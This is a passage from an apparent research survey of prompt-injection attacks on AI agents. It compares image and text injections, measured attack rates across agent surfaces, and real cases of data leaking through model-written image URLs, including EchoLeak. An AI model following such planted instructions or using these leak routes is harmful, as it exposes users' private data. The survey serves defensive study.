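| Qwen3.6-plus | 60.8% | 22.3% |
| Kimi-K2.6 | 50.8% | 12.3% |
| Grok 4.3 | 32.3% | 23.8% |
| GPT-5.4 mini | 29.2% | 7.7% |
| GPT-5.4 nano | 14.6% | 0.0% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 1.5% | 0.8% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.8% | 0.0% |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 0.0% | 0.0% |

Instructions were less effective as pictures than as text against every model that the text had fooled. The difference persisted when Zhang and colleagues used adaptive attackers, including seven human experts who spent 144 hours looking for attacks. The attacks they all found succeeded against Claude Haiku 4.5 97.6% of the time as text and 9.5% as pictures. Against GPT-5.4 mini, the rates were 83.3% and 31.0%.

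Zhang and colleagues attribute the difference to training, in which models learn to follow instructions mainly from typed examples and learn to treat pictures as things to describe. The difference was largely absent in models that had not yet learned to follow instructions, and it shrank when the researchers trained a model on harmless instructions in pictures. Developers who train agents to work from screenshots might therefore unintentionally weaken this protection.

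Presenting a document as an image instead of text protects some models from planted commands more than others. Liu, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *What Survives the Shift from Text to Pixels?*, gave six models the same 191 documents in both forms. The planted commands told the model to add a marker to its answer, change the answer's format or replace the answer with a fixed phrase, but none asked for a tool action. GPT-5-nano added the marker in 78% of text trials and no image trials. But Qwen3-VL-8B still replaced its answer in 77.96% of image trials, compared with 98.73% of text trials. Larger type and higher resolution both made the image commands more effective. Letting the attacker try up to eight commands per document largely removed the protection in the marker and format tests for Qwen and Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, but not for GPT-5-nano.

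Liu, Xu and colleagues found that models could often copy out a command from an image and recognise it as a command without carrying it out, so misreading the image does not explain all the failed attacks.

This seems to conflict with Chen and Ghadiyaram's results, in which on-screen text often misled Gemini more than typed text did, but the experiments probably tested different things. Words on a video frame look like evidence about the video, and a model may accept a false statement in a picture more readily than it follows a command there.

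The same command is generally less effective at making a model act when it appears in a picture than in text. Pictures may still be riskier in a particular product, because text filters and users can miss the instructions in them. As a hypothetical example, suppose a filter blocks 90% of typed instructions but none in pictures, and the model follows 40% of the typed instructions that reach it and 20% of those in pictures. An attacker would then succeed in 4% of attempts with text and 20% with pictures.

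In both comparisons of commands, the researchers turned text into plain, readable images themselves, so neither covers images designed by an attacker, such as those Trail of Bits used. Zhang and colleagues state that their method offers no protection against image-based attacks. Converting incoming text to images may therefore make an application safer against planted text, but accepting images from strangers still gives attackers another way to target it.

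## Measured attack rates for coding, tool, desktop and browser agents

Companies that test complete agents usually report results by surface, the kind of environment an agent works in. Coding agents work on software projects, tool-use agents call services such as a calendar or an online shop, computer-use agents operate a desktop that they see through screenshots, and browser-use agents work on websites. One surface can include several channels. For example, a coding agent may read source files, bug reports and web pages during one task.

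Testers count successes in two ways. The attempt-level rate is the share of all attempts that succeed. The scenario-level rate is the share of test scenarios in which at least one attempt succeeds. If a tester makes 200 attempts in each of ten scenarios and succeeds exactly once in each, the attempt-level rate is 0.5% and the scenario-level rate is 100%.

### The Gray Swan competition

Many of the published figures come from Gray Swan, a company that tests AI systems by attacking them. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) describes a three-week public competition that Gray Swan held with several AI developers and the British and American governments' AI institutes. The 464 participants competed for $40,000 in prizes and made about 272,000 attack attempts against 13 models. About 3% of the attempts succeeded.

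The organisers wrote 41 scenarios: 18 for tool use, 15 for coding and eight for computer use. In each, the attacker controlled one piece of content that an outsider could plausibly write, such as a comment in a code repository, a customer review or an advert on a web page. The attacker could read the conversation up to that point and knew which action to trigger. Someone emailing a stranger's assistant would usually know neither, so Dziemian and colleagues call their rates an upper bound on how vulnerable the agents are within a single turn, though more skilled or persistent attackers than the contestants could still do better.

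In most scenarios, an attack counted as successful only if the agent carried out the harmful action and its final answer gave no sign of it. The official rates therefore understate how often the agents did something harmful. Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro had the highest official rate in the competition, 8.5%, but it carried out the harmful action in about 16% of attempts. About half of those didn't count because the final answer gave some sign of the action. Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.5 had the lowest official rate, 0.5%. For leaks, the rate of harmful actions is more relevant, because the agent can't take back private data once it has sent it, even if its final answer discloses the leak.

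Across all the models, attackers succeeded in 4.82% of attempts in tool use, 3.13% in computer use and 2.51% in coding. Dziemian and colleagues suggest that the coding rate was lower because those scenarios reused real transcripts, which may resemble the models' safety training material. Although the average rate was higher in tool use, Gemini 2.5 Pro and Opus 4.5 were more vulnerable in computer use (16.2% and 1.1%) than in tool use (8.9% and 0.6%). The computer-use average excludes three models that cannot process images, so the three averages do not cover the same set of models.

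A model's general ability was a poor predictor of its resistance to attack. Gemini 2.5 Pro and Kimi K2 both scored around 85% on a test of difficult science questions, but attacks succeeded 8.5% of the time against Gemini 2.5 Pro and 4.8% against Kimi K2. Across all the models, the correlation between test score and attack success rate was weak and not statistically significant.

### Replaying the attacks on newer models

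Gray Swan also turns successful attacks into a benchmark by replaying them on other models. Dziemian and colleagues selected 2,679 attacks, with at most nine for each combination of model and scenario, and ran them on the 13 competition models and two others. The replayed attacks succeeded much more often than the original attempts because only successful attacks were selected. Gemini 2.5 Pro's rate rose from 8.5% to 45%, and Opus 4.5's rose from 0.5% to 2.5%.

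The results also depended on which model an attack had originally worked on. The 44 selected attacks that had worked on Opus 4.5 succeeded in 44 to 81% of replays on the other models. None of those that had worked on Qwen3 VL, one of the weakest models, succeeded on Opus 4.5. The choice of attacks can therefore make a benchmark much easier or harder.

Gray Swan has since updated the benchmark with attacks from newer competitions. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1, a safety report from September, gives results on 1,804 attacks in 37 scenarios. Gray Swan chose attacks that worked on many models. The harmful actions included sending out private data, deleting data and making payments. The table shows the estimated chance that an attacker succeeds at least once within a given number of attempts.

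| Model | 1 attempt | 10 attempts | 15 attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 0.1% | 0.7% | 1.0% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.4% | 3.6% | 4.8% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 0.6% | 4.9% | 6.5% |

Google's Gemini 3.7 Flash had the lowest attack success rate among other companies' models, at 9.2% within 15 attempts. Most of the rest were between 24% and 53%.

Fable 5.1's attack success rate within 15 attempts was 4.1% in computer use, 0.3% in coding and 0.0% in tool use. These rates are weak evidence that computer use is the riskiest surface, because only five attacks succeeded in 7,124 runs across all three, and a few more successes in coding could have changed the comparison. Anthropic's *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (2026) announced Fable 5.1's successor in November. Anthropic released Claude Opus 5.5 in late September. The model's *System Card* (2026) reports results similar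 to or better than those of Opus 5 on every prompt injection test it includes, but adds that the model is more likely than its predecessors to follow some malicious instructions.

### Comparing scores between companies

Gray Swan scores from two companies' safety reports are comparable only if both companies used the same version of the benchmark, the same number of attempts and equivalent safeguards. For its September report, Anthropic changed the benchmark by adding nine scenarios and 670 attacks and dropping older models that contestants had targeted in recent competitions. Contestants tailor their attacks to the models they target, so those models tend to do worse on the resulting benchmark than models that did not take part. Gray Swan tested the Claude models without their defences against prompt injection but tested other companies' models through those companies' public services, which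 may include such defences.

Other published figures are even harder to compare. VentureBeat reports that OpenAI gave GPT-5.5 a robustness score of 0.963, down from 0.998 for GPT-5.4-thinking, where higher is better. The score covers known attacks on one surface, so subtracting it from 1 would not give a rate comparable with Anthropic's. TechRepublic's *OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) reports that in OpenAI's later results for GPT-5.6, attacks typed directly into a chat rarely worked, while attacks through tools and outside content succeeded more often. A low attack rate for a chatbot is therefore weak evidence that an agent is safe.

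Google's safety report for Gemini 3 gives no attack success rate, as VentureBeat notes. *How we estimate the risk from prompt injection attacks on AI systems* describes the company's testing method, in which the planted instruction has to extract sensitive information from a range of conversations that the attacker has not seen. Attackers in Gray Swan's competition could read the conversation first, so the same success rate would be more worrying in Google's test.

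Even testing several companies' models with the same attacker may not rank them fairly. The *Beam Model Technical Report* (2026) includes results from Shade, Gray Swan's automated attacker, on 85 recorded tasks for coding agents and personal assistants. The report advises caution in comparing models because Gray Swan had trained Shade against Claude models. An attacker trained this way may do worse against other companies' models even if they are no safer.

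### What repeated attempts add

The 15-attempt figures depend on how successful attacks are distributed between scenarios, as well as on how common they are. Fable 5's rate was 0.6% for a single attempt. If every attempt were independent and had the same chance of success, the chance of at least one success in 15 would be:

$$1 - (1 - 0.006)^{15} = 1 - 0.994^{15} \approx 8.6\%$$

The reported figure was 6.5%. Rounding cannot explain the difference, because even a single-attempt rate of 0.55%, the lowest that rounds to 0.6%, would give about 7.9%. The likely explanation is that successes cluster in certain scenarios. Extra attempts then add little, because they either repeat a success where the model is weak or usually fail where it is strong.

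For example, suppose a model falls for 6% of attacks in one scenario out of ten and for none in the other nine. Its average rate is 0.6%. After 15 attempts in each scenario, the chance that at least one succeeds is 1 − 0.94<sup>15</sup>, or about 60%, in the weak scenario and zero elsewhere, so the average is about 6%. That average understates the risk to anyone using the agent for the task in the weak scenario.

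### Attackers trained on the test scenarios

Testing a model with old attacks can make it look safer than it is, because a real attacker can invent new ones. Anthropic therefore also uses Shade, which improves its attacks through automated search, reinforcement learning (training by reward) and human advice. For the coding test, Gray Swan trained Shade on 40 scenarios with earlier Claude models as targets, then ran it unchanged on newer models in the same scenarios. Shade had therefore adapted to the test and to Claude models in general, but not to Fable 5.1. Anthropic's computer-use test has 14 scenarios. In both tests, Shade makes 200 attempts per scenario.

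For the browser test, professional testers developed attacks against the older Claude Opus 4.7, and Anthropic then tried them on newer models, with ten attempts in each of 110 scenarios. The table shows Fable 5.1's results in all these tests. The extra safeguards are tools that check for planted instructions and, in the browser test only, another tool that blocks dangerous actions.

| Test | Successful attempts, no extra safeguards | Scenarios with a success, no extra safeguards | Successful attempts, extra safeguards | Scenarios with a success, extra safeguards |
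|---|---|---|---|---|
| Coding, earlier version of Shade | 9.26% | 31 of 40 | 2.05% | 18 of 40 |
| Coding, stronger version of Shade | 56.87% | 38 of 40 | 12.80% | 36 of 40 |
| Computer use, Shade | 0.07% | 2 of 14 | 0.07% | 2 of 14 |
| Browser use, attacks developed on Opus 4.7 | 2.64% | 10 of 110 | 0% | 0 of 110 |

Computer use looked much riskier than coding in the replayed attacks, but Shade's results showed the opposite. The stronger version of Shade succeeded in more than half of its coding attempts, while Shade succeeded in only two of 2,800 computer-use attempts.

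The ranking of browser and computer use also depends on the measure. Without extra safeguards, 2.64% of attack attempts succeeded against browser use and 0.07% against computer use. But attackers succeeded at least once in 14% of computer-use scenarios and 9% of browser scenarios. They had 200 attempts per computer-use scenario and ten per browser scenario, so the scenario-level rates are not a fair comparison either.

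Anthropic regards the stronger coding attacker as a stress test, not an estimate of what users face. A real attacker could not usually practise on the victim's exact task, and someone who sent 200 malicious messages would risk detection. But an attacker can send one message to thousands of people. Popular coding agents also perform many similar tasks, so an attacker could practise on a similar set-up without contacting the victim.

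### Requests answered by an older model

Fable 5.1 did not answer every request in these tests. Anthropic uses automated filters, called classifiers, to detect attempts to misuse the model for hacking or biological weapons. When the hacking classifier flags a request, the older Claude Opus 4.8 answers instead. Anthropic included this handover in its September tests because users experience it too.

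In the test with the stronger version of Shade, every successful attack was against Opus 4.8, which answered about 64% of the requests. None succeeded in the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered itself. Overall, 56.87% of attempts succeeded, so Opus 4.8 must have followed the planted instruction in nearly nine out of ten of the requests it answered.

These results do not show that Fable 5.1 would have resisted the attacks if it had answered every request. The classifier sent the requests that looked most like hacking to Opus 4.8, and those requests may also have contained the most effective attacks. Opus 4.8 may have been at a further disadvantage if it was one of the earlier models Gray Swan used to train Shade. Only a test with the handover switched off could show how Fable 5.1 would have performed.

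Older figures suggest that the handover to Opus 4.8 can greatly affect Fable 5's measured attack rate. According to Digital Applied (2026), a company blog, Anthropic reported in June that adaptive coding attacks succeeded 0.41% of the time against the model behind Fable 5 and 2.09% of the time against Opus 4.8. In September, Fable 5's rate with the earlier version of Shade was 9.70%, and Opus 4.8 answered 99% of the requests that received a valid response. The handover probably explains part of the increase, but the attacker or the test must also have changed, because 9.70% is far above even Opus 4.8's June rate.

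In the browser test, 21 of the 29 successful attacks on Fable 5.1 came after a handover to another model, which was Opus 4.8 in 20 cases. Opus 4.8 took over in about 11% of attempts, and roughly one in six of those attempts succeeded. Without a handover, fewer than 1% of attempts succeeded. VentureBeat had already reported that attacks on Opus 4.8 without safeguards succeeded in 31.5% of attempts across 129 browser scenarios.

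The handover made little difference on the replayed benchmark, where an older model answered 23% of requests, including about half of those in coding. Only one attack against it succeeded in 1,653 runs. Shade's success rate was nearly nine in ten, which shows how much the results depend on the attacker. Opus 4.8 could resist attacks from past competitions and still be highly vulnerable to an attacker that had practised on the test.

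### What Anthropic's safeguards changed

Anthropic's prompt injection probes scan what an agent's tools return, such as web pages and files, and flag anything that looks like a planted instruction before the model acts on it. Auto mode, the default permission setting in the coding agent Claude Code, adds a classifier that blocks potentially dangerous tool calls, so an attack has to get past both checks.

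The probes reduced the success rate of the stronger version of Shade against Fable 5.1 from 56.87% to 12.80% of attempts, but the number of scenarios with at least one success fell only from 38 to 36. An attacker with one attempt would do much worse against the probes, but one with 200 attempts would still succeed in most scenarios. This table shows the same test for four models, all with extended reasoning on.

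| Model | Successful attempts, no probes | Scenarios with a success, no probes | Successful attempts, probes | Scenarios with a success, probes |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 56.87% | 38 of 40 | 12.80% | 36 of 40 |
| Claude Fable 5 | 86.87% | 40 of 40 | 34.09% | 39 of 40 |
| Claude Opus 5 | 90.93% | 40 of 40 | 18.21% | 40 of 40 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 19.47% | 36 of 40 | 15.76% | 35 of 40 |

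Probes reduced the attack success rate much less for Sonnet 5 than for Opus 5, so a developer cannot assume that the same safeguard will reduce risk by the same proportion for every model. In computer use, probes lowered Fable 5's rate from 2.50% to 1.93%. They did not change Fable 5.1's rate, which was already close to zero, at two successes in 2,800 attempts.

The most encouraging result came from the browser test, where auto mode reduced Fable 5.1's rate from 2.64% to 0%. Auto mode combines the probes with the action classifier, so the result does not show which stopped the attacks. The comparison also overstates the benefit of switching auto mode on. The test used Claude Cowork, which always runs the probes, so no Cowork user would face the 2.64% rate. For Fable 5, one attack in 1,100 still succeeded with auto mode on, after a handover to Opus 4.8.

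If something never happens in *n* independent trials, a common statistical rule of thumb is that its true rate could still be as high as about 3/*n*. Attackers succeeded in none of the 110 browser scenarios, so if these are treated as a random sample of tasks, attackers could still succeed within ten attempts in up to about 2.7% of such tasks. The attackers also developed their attacks on an older model rather than against auto mode itself.

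The coding results do not include auto mode's action classifier, so the 12.80% rate may overstate the risk to someone using Claude Code with its default settings. Auto mode reduced the rate to zero in browsers, but that does not show it would do the same for coding. A coding agent has legitimate reasons to run commands and change files, which may make harmful actions harder for a classifier to recognise.

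### The reverse pattern in February

In Anthropic's February safety report, seven months before the Fable 5.1 results, Claude Opus 4.6 was more vulnerable to attacks on a desktop than in a restricted coding environment. According to VentureBeat's coverage of the report, attacks in the coding environment never succeeded, even with 200 attempts. On a desktop, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time without safeguards. Within 200 attempts, the success rate reached 78.6% without safeguards and 57.1% with them.

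Those last two percentages equal 11 and eight out of 14, and September's computer-use test had 14 scenarios, so they are probably the shares of scenarios in which at least one attack succeeded. If so, the number of desktop scenarios with a successful attack fell from 11 for Opus 4.6 to two for Fable 5.1, both without extra safeguards. The models have very likely improved, but the attacker and other test details may also have changed between the two reports.

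The attack success rate for coding moved in the opposite direction, from zero to more than half of all attempts. In September, Gray Swan used a stronger attacker with longer training on the test scenarios, and an older model answered most of the requests, so the increase does not mean that newer Claude models are worse at resisting attacks on code. The difference between coding and desktop agents in February did not last, so it would have been an unreliable basis for giving coding agents less protection.

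### What a rate for one surface leaves out

In Shade's results, the attack rate was 56.87% for coding agents, which mainly read text, and 0.07% for computer-use agents, which take in screenshots. Controlled tests have found that typed commands generally work better than the same commands in pictures. But Shade's coding and computer-use tests also differ in their tasks, the tools available to the agent, the attacker's training and the share of requests that went to Opus 4.8. Any of these could account for much of the gap, so the results alone don't show that text is the more dangerous form of input.

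Dziemian and colleagues ranked the strategies that contestants used and found almost no overlap between the most successful ones for tool use, coding and computer use. A surface may therefore have a low attack rate only because nobody has yet found a method that suits it. But some weaknesses extend well beyond one type of task. A single template, with only small changes, worked in 21 of the 41 scenarios and on nine models.

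Most of these tests place the planted instruction directly in the agent's path, and in Anthropic's browser test the model always encountered it. The rates therefore mainly measure obedience, not reach, in the three-factor product. They also do not isolate the risk to private data, because many of the harmful actions are not leaks. For example, one of the competition's email scenarios required the agent only to mark an urgent message as read.

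Measuring how much the form of the input matters on a given surface would require keeping the task, tools, model and attacker the same and changing only how the instruction appears. Anthropic's browser test nearly has the data needed for this comparison, because its agents encounter some attacks in screenshots and others in page text, but the published results combine the two.

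## Images that load when an answer is displayed

Since 2023, security researchers have repeatedly shown that chat and coding products can leak private data through the pictures in their answers.

### From the model's text to another server's log

The model follows a planted instruction and writes the code for an image on the attacker's site, with private text at the end of the image's address. When the application displays the answer, the browser requests the image, and the attacker's server logs the address. The image does not have to appear. Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* describes a test in which the chat showed no image but the request still reached the researchers' server.

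Ordinary web pages often load images from other sites, but this is less risky because the page's author usually chose the addresses in advance. A model composes the address while it answers, when its context may contain both private data and a stranger's instruction.

The leak needs no tool call because the image code is part of the answer. An agent's software typically asks for approval when the model requests an action, such as sending an email or running a command, but it treats the answer as text to display. *Takedown* (2025), a study of attacks on coding agents, points out that the renderer does not require the user's approval. Network filters on the servers that run the model also miss the image request, because it comes from the user's own computer.

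The security company VerSprite found an example of this gap in Continue, a coding assistant. *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Continue* describes a test in which the user approved Continue's request to fetch a web page that contained a planted instruction. The instruction led the assistant to read a file of secrets and display a picture whose address contained them, and no prompt mentioned the picture.

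### ChatGPT and Bing Chat in 2023

*New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, by the software engineer Roman Samoilenko (April 2023), describes how a script on an attacker's website could leak text from a ChatGPT conversation. The script added an instruction to whatever a visitor copied. If the visitor pasted the text into ChatGPT without checking it, ChatGPT added a nearly invisible picture to its answer, with text from the chat in the picture's address. The instruction could also make ChatGPT do this in later answers, so that the attacker received each new question.

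Samoilenko found the attack unreliable. It could easily extract a user's previous prompts or code, but rarely passwords or API keys. If ChatGPT answered slowly, the user might also notice the strange text as it appeared. Samoilenko advised OpenAI to stop ChatGPT from displaying markdown images.

*OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, a post on Johann Rehberger's security blog Embrace The Red, describes OpenAI's first step toward a fix in December 2023. ChatGPT's web version began checking with an OpenAI server that each image's address was safe before loading it. The iPhone app lacked this check and remained vulnerable to the original attack. OpenAI had not published its criteria, and Rehberger found that the check still allowed some images from an outside server, enough to leak very small amounts of data. Willison (2023), commenting on the post, called the fix half-baked.

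OpenAI added further protection around August 2025 and explained its approach in January 2026. ChatGPT now loads a picture automatically only if a separate web crawler has already found that exact address on the public web. The crawler has no access to users' conversations, so OpenAI argues that an address the crawler has recorded is much less likely to contain a user's private data. If the crawler has not recorded the address, ChatGPT looks for another source or warns the user before opening the address.

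Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* calls this a significant improvement, though small leaks remain possible. Rehberger was also concerned that some developers at OpenAI might not know about the protection and leave it out of their products.

Microsoft fixed the same weakness in Bing Chat within about two months. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* explains that the assistant could read the web page a user had open, so an attacker could plant an instruction in a comment or an advert on that page. In Rehberger's demonstration, the conversation continued normally for two turns before the image appeared. The image's URL contained a summary of the page and the conversation, along with a secret from elsewhere on the page.

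Rehberger reported the flaw on 8 April 2023, and Microsoft confirmed a fix on 15 June. The attack no longer worked, at least partly because Microsoft had introduced a content security policy that let images load from only four Microsoft domains.

### Coding assistants from 2024 to 2026

GitHub Copilot Chat, an extension for the code editor VS Code, had a similar flaw. Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat* describes an instruction hidden in a source code file. When a user asked about the file, the assistant displayed an image whose address contained information from earlier in the conversation. Rehberger reported the flaw on 25 February 2024 and was told on 12 June that it had been fixed. His tests suggested that Copilot Chat no longer displayed markdown images at all, but Willison, commenting on the same post, describes the fix as blocking images from untrusted domains.

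The Copilot Chat attack took information already in the conversation. An attacker can get more from an agent that can open files, because the planted instruction can make it read a file first. Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Amp Code* shows this with Amp, Sourcegraph's coding agent. A comment in a source file led Amp to open a file of passwords and keys, then send out the contents through an image. Rehberger also tried a web page prepared earlier for other demonstrations, and it worked on Amp too, so an attacker may need little new work to target another product with the same flaw. Sourcegraph fixed Amp soon after Rehberger contacted it on 14 June 2025.

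Cline, another coding agent, had the same flaw. Rehberger reported it on 29 May 2025, but its developers still had not fixed it when he published it more than 90 days later, according to Embrace The Red's *Cline*. The post therefore omits the main part of the test instruction. Users could require approval before Cline read a file, which would limit what an attacker could add to the conversation. This would not protect secrets already in the conversation, since Cline could display the image without approval.

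Continue's developers released a fix on 21 August 2025, the day after VerSprite reported the flaw. The assistant now asks before it loads an external image, and it restricts access to certain files.

In 2026, researchers found the flaw in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, which had gained features for everyday office work. PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* describes a user who asked Codex to review their emails, one of which contained a planted instruction. Codex displayed an image whose address sent the full contents of other emails, including legal correspondence and financial plans, to an online form that the attacker controlled. The user took no further action, and Codex did not show the emails' contents while it reviewed them. PromptArmor reported the flaw on 21 April, and OpenAI has since fixed it.

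*CVE-2026-14898* (2026), an entry in the CVE Program's public record of software flaws, describes the same weakness in the Codex desktop app for macOS. It credits other researchers, so it is unclear whether this is the flaw that PromptArmor found. OpenAI's fix disables remote images in markdown. The entry, published on 6 July, lists no known attacks outside research. In it, the American cybersecurity agency CISA rates the flaw's severity at 6.5 out of 10 and marks the attack as requiring user interaction. This probably refers to the user's original request, since the image loads without a click.

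The AI chat in Eclipse Theia, a platform for building code editors, loaded images from any address, so an instruction planted in a malicious project folder could cause a leak. GitLab's June advisory, *CVE-2026-22551* (2026), explains that version 1.71.0 turns off AI features in folders the user has not marked as trusted. This keeps the planted instruction from reaching the model, but it would not necessarily help if an instruction reached a trusted project from elsewhere.

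The table lists these cases in the order researchers first reported them, where the date is known. Most were demonstrations by the people who found the flaws, and none of the reports measures how often an attack would succeed against ordinary users.

| Product | Data exposed | Fix | Date of fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT, web version | Prompts and code from the chat | Check on each picture's address, later strengthened | December 2023 (partial); strengthened around August 2025 |
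| Bing Chat | The conversation and other text on the open page | Content security policy allowing four Microsoft domains | 15 June 2023 |
| GitHub Copilot Chat in VS Code | Chat history | Images blocked, at least from untrusted domains | 12 June 2024 |
| Cline | Chat contents and files, including secrets | None when Rehberger published the flaw | None reported |
| Amp | Chat contents and files, including secrets | Not described | Soon after 14 June 2025 |
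| Continue | Chat contents and files, including secrets | Approval before external images load; limits on file access | 21 August 2025 |
| Codex desktop app for macOS | API keys, source code and data from connected services | Remote images disabled | By 6 July 2026 |
| Eclipse Theia | Project files and chat contents | AI features disabled in untrusted folders | By 18 June 2026 |

Vendors do not always accept that such a leak is a product flaw. In October 2025, Checkmarx reported that Copilot Chat could again leak an API key through an image. Microsoft closed the report on 4 November without a fix. It said the attack needed several non-default actions by the user, did not work reliably across environments and triggered warnings. It also expected users to review and trust the code they work with.

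Google's position differs between its products. Checkmarx quotes the company as saying that Gemini does not display external images, which prevents this kind of leak. But a researcher quoted in Willison's *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”* said that Google had classified a similar report about its coding tool, Antigravity, as intended behaviour.

### What the fixes cost

Blocking all external images prevents data from leaking through image requests, even if the model follows the attacker's instructions. However, users also lose useful pictures hosted on other sites. This matters little for a coding assistant, but a travel assistant that can't show hotels is noticeably worse. The block also has to cover every format that can include an image in an answer, not just markdown.

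A content security policy lists the domains from which a page may load images and other content. The application's server sends the policy to the browser with the page. If an answer links to an image on any other domain, the browser does not request it. Microsoft calls such defences deterministic and prefers them where possible because they do not depend on how the model behaves. Outside researchers can also read the policy, whereas Rehberger had to guess at the rules behind OpenAI's first check.

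The policy blocks legitimate images from unlisted sites, and someone has to keep the list up to date. A listed domain can still leak data if an attacker can receive data through it, as *EchoLeak* (2025) describes. Content security policies also work only where a browser, or an app built on one, displays the answer. A phone app that displays answers another way needs its own control.

Another option is an image proxy, a server run by the vendor that fetches each picture and passes it to the user's browser. The browser never contacts the outside site, so the user's network address stays hidden. However, a proxy alone does not prevent the leak, because if it requests an address containing private text, the outside server still receives that text. To prevent this, the proxy has to reject addresses that the model has composed and serve only pictures approved beforehand.

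The vendor also has to run the proxy and pay for its traffic, and a design mistake can let data leak again. GitHub normally uses a proxy to serve outside images safely, but it disabled images completely in the Copilot Chat on its website after Legit Security's *CamoLeak* showed that an attacker could send out private code through GitHub's own infrastructure.

Continue now asks the user before loading each external image. This keeps pictures available, but the user has to judge a web address that may be long and hard to read. OpenAI's check for public addresses requires fewer decisions from users, but the company has to maintain a large record of the web, and users see warnings about new or private pictures that its crawler has not found.

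The team that tests AI systems for NVIDIA was still finding this flaw in 2025, more than two years after Rehberger publicised it. Security specialists disagree about which fix a developer should try first. The NVIDIA team puts an image content security policy first and treats disabling links, images and other active content as a last resort. In the report on Copilot Chat, Rehberger recommended displaying no images or links, with a list of allowed domains only if the product needs them. For an agent that can read secrets and rarely needs to show pictures, Rehberger's order seems safer because it avoids the risk of mistakes in the list.

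### A blocked image that loaded on a developer's log page

An application can block a dangerous image and still leave the model's original text in its records. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* shows how this can leak data when a developer later reads those records.

PromptArmor built a test application to help bank staff check customers' identities. It combined customers' personal details with information from several sources, including web text that contained a planted instruction. The model followed the instruction and wrote code for an image whose address contained a customer's data. A second model reviewing the answers flagged and blocked this one, so the bank's staff never saw it and no data leaked.

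The leak happened when a developer opened the flagged conversation in OpenAI's log viewer, a web page where developers review what their applications' models have written. The log viewer rendered the answer as markdown and loaded the picture, and the request for the picture sent the customer's passport details and financial information to the attacker's server. The application's defence may have made the leak more likely, because developers have a reason to open flagged conversations.

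PromptArmor reported the problem on 17 November 2025 through Bugcrowd, a company that handles such reports for OpenAI. Bugcrowd closed the report as "not applicable" on 4 December, and OpenAI did not see it until PromptArmor published its findings in January 2026. On 22 January, OpenAI reopened the report and said that a fix was under way. PromptArmor's timeline ends there, with no date for a completed fix.

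A stronger image defence in the bank's application would not have helped, because a content security policy applies only to the page it comes with, and removing the image code from the displayed answer leaves it in OpenAI's log. PromptArmor found the same weakness in screens developers use to preview and test new AI tools. Every place that displays a model's output therefore needs the same restriction on images, including phone apps, saved conversations, support dashboards and emails that an agent sends.

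The restriction can vary by interface. A chat window may need to show some images, but a log page can show the model's output as plain text. Developers would lose very little, since someone investigating a suspicious answer needs to see exactly what the model wrote. In 2023, Rehberger suggested that OpenAI run ChatGPT's address check on its servers instead of in each app, so that every version would be protected at once.

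## Image leaks through approved domains

A chat page can show outside images only if its content security policy allows some outside domains. In 2025 and 2026, security researchers demonstrated four flaws that let private data leave through images on allowed domains. Two were in Microsoft 365 Copilot, one in Salesforce's Agentforce and one in the email application Superhuman. The vendors have since fixed all four.

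| Flaw | Entry | Data exposed | Exit | Failed assumption | Fix |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak (Microsoft 365 Copilot) | Email | Anything in Copilot's context | A Teams service that fetches outside addresses | A request to a Microsoft domain stays with Microsoft | Server-side update, May 2025 |
| ForcedLeak (Agentforce) | Public web form | Customer records | An expired domain that anyone could buy | An approved domain keeps its owner | Domain recovered and list corrected; new limits on agents' links from 8 September 2025 |
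| Superhuman | Email | Dozens of other emails | A form on a Google domain | Only Google can read what a Google domain receives | Features disabled, then patched, December 2025 to January 2026 |
| SearchLeak (Microsoft 365 Copilot) | Link to Copilot's search page | Emails, calendar and files | A Bing service that fetches outside pictures | A request to a Microsoft domain stays with Microsoft | Server-side update, early June 2026 |

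### EchoLeak: a Microsoft service that passed data on

Microsoft 365 Copilot works inside Outlook, Word, Teams and other Office applications. When an employee asks a question, it searches the mailbox, files, internal websites and chat history that the employee can open, and adds relevant material to the model's context. Although only employees can use Copilot, anyone can email them, so a stranger's text can end up in the context next to confidential files.

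In January 2025, researchers at Aim Security discovered that such an email could make Copilot leak data. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) gives their account of the flaw. It is publicly recorded as CVE-2025-32711, with a severity score of 9.3 out of 10, according to TechRadar's *Microsoft Copilot targeted in first “zero-click” attack on an AI agent*.

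The planted instructions took effect when the employee later asked Copilot about an ordinary work topic and Copilot retrieved the email as relevant, even if the employee had never opened the email or clicked anything. In Aim's tests, this happened with questions on various topics, though Ravia gives no success rate. Ravia and *EchoLeak*, a case study by Pavan Reddy and Aditya Sanjay Gujral, both describe the user asking something first. Goldman (2025), in *New Microsoft Copilot flaw signals broader risk of AI agents being hacked*, is less detailed than Ravia and describes Copilot as scanning mail in the background, which suggests that the attack needed no question.

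Everything in the context was at risk, including the conversation, any emails and files that Copilot had fetched, and the names of the user and the organisation. The instructions left the model to pick the most sensitive item, so the attacker did not need to know what the company's files contained.

Copilot had several safeguards, and each of them failed:

- A classifier checks incoming content for planted instructions before the model reads it. It did not flag the email. Ravia points out that such classifiers need a great deal of training data and that good examples of real attacks are scarce.
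- A filter removes links to outside sites from Copilot's answers, but it missed some.
- The same filter applies to outside images, and it missed some of those too.
- The content security policy blocked images from unapproved domains, but the researchers found an approved one that would pass data on.
- Copilot normally refers to the sources behind an answer. The researchers got it to leave out the malicious email, which made the leak harder to trace.

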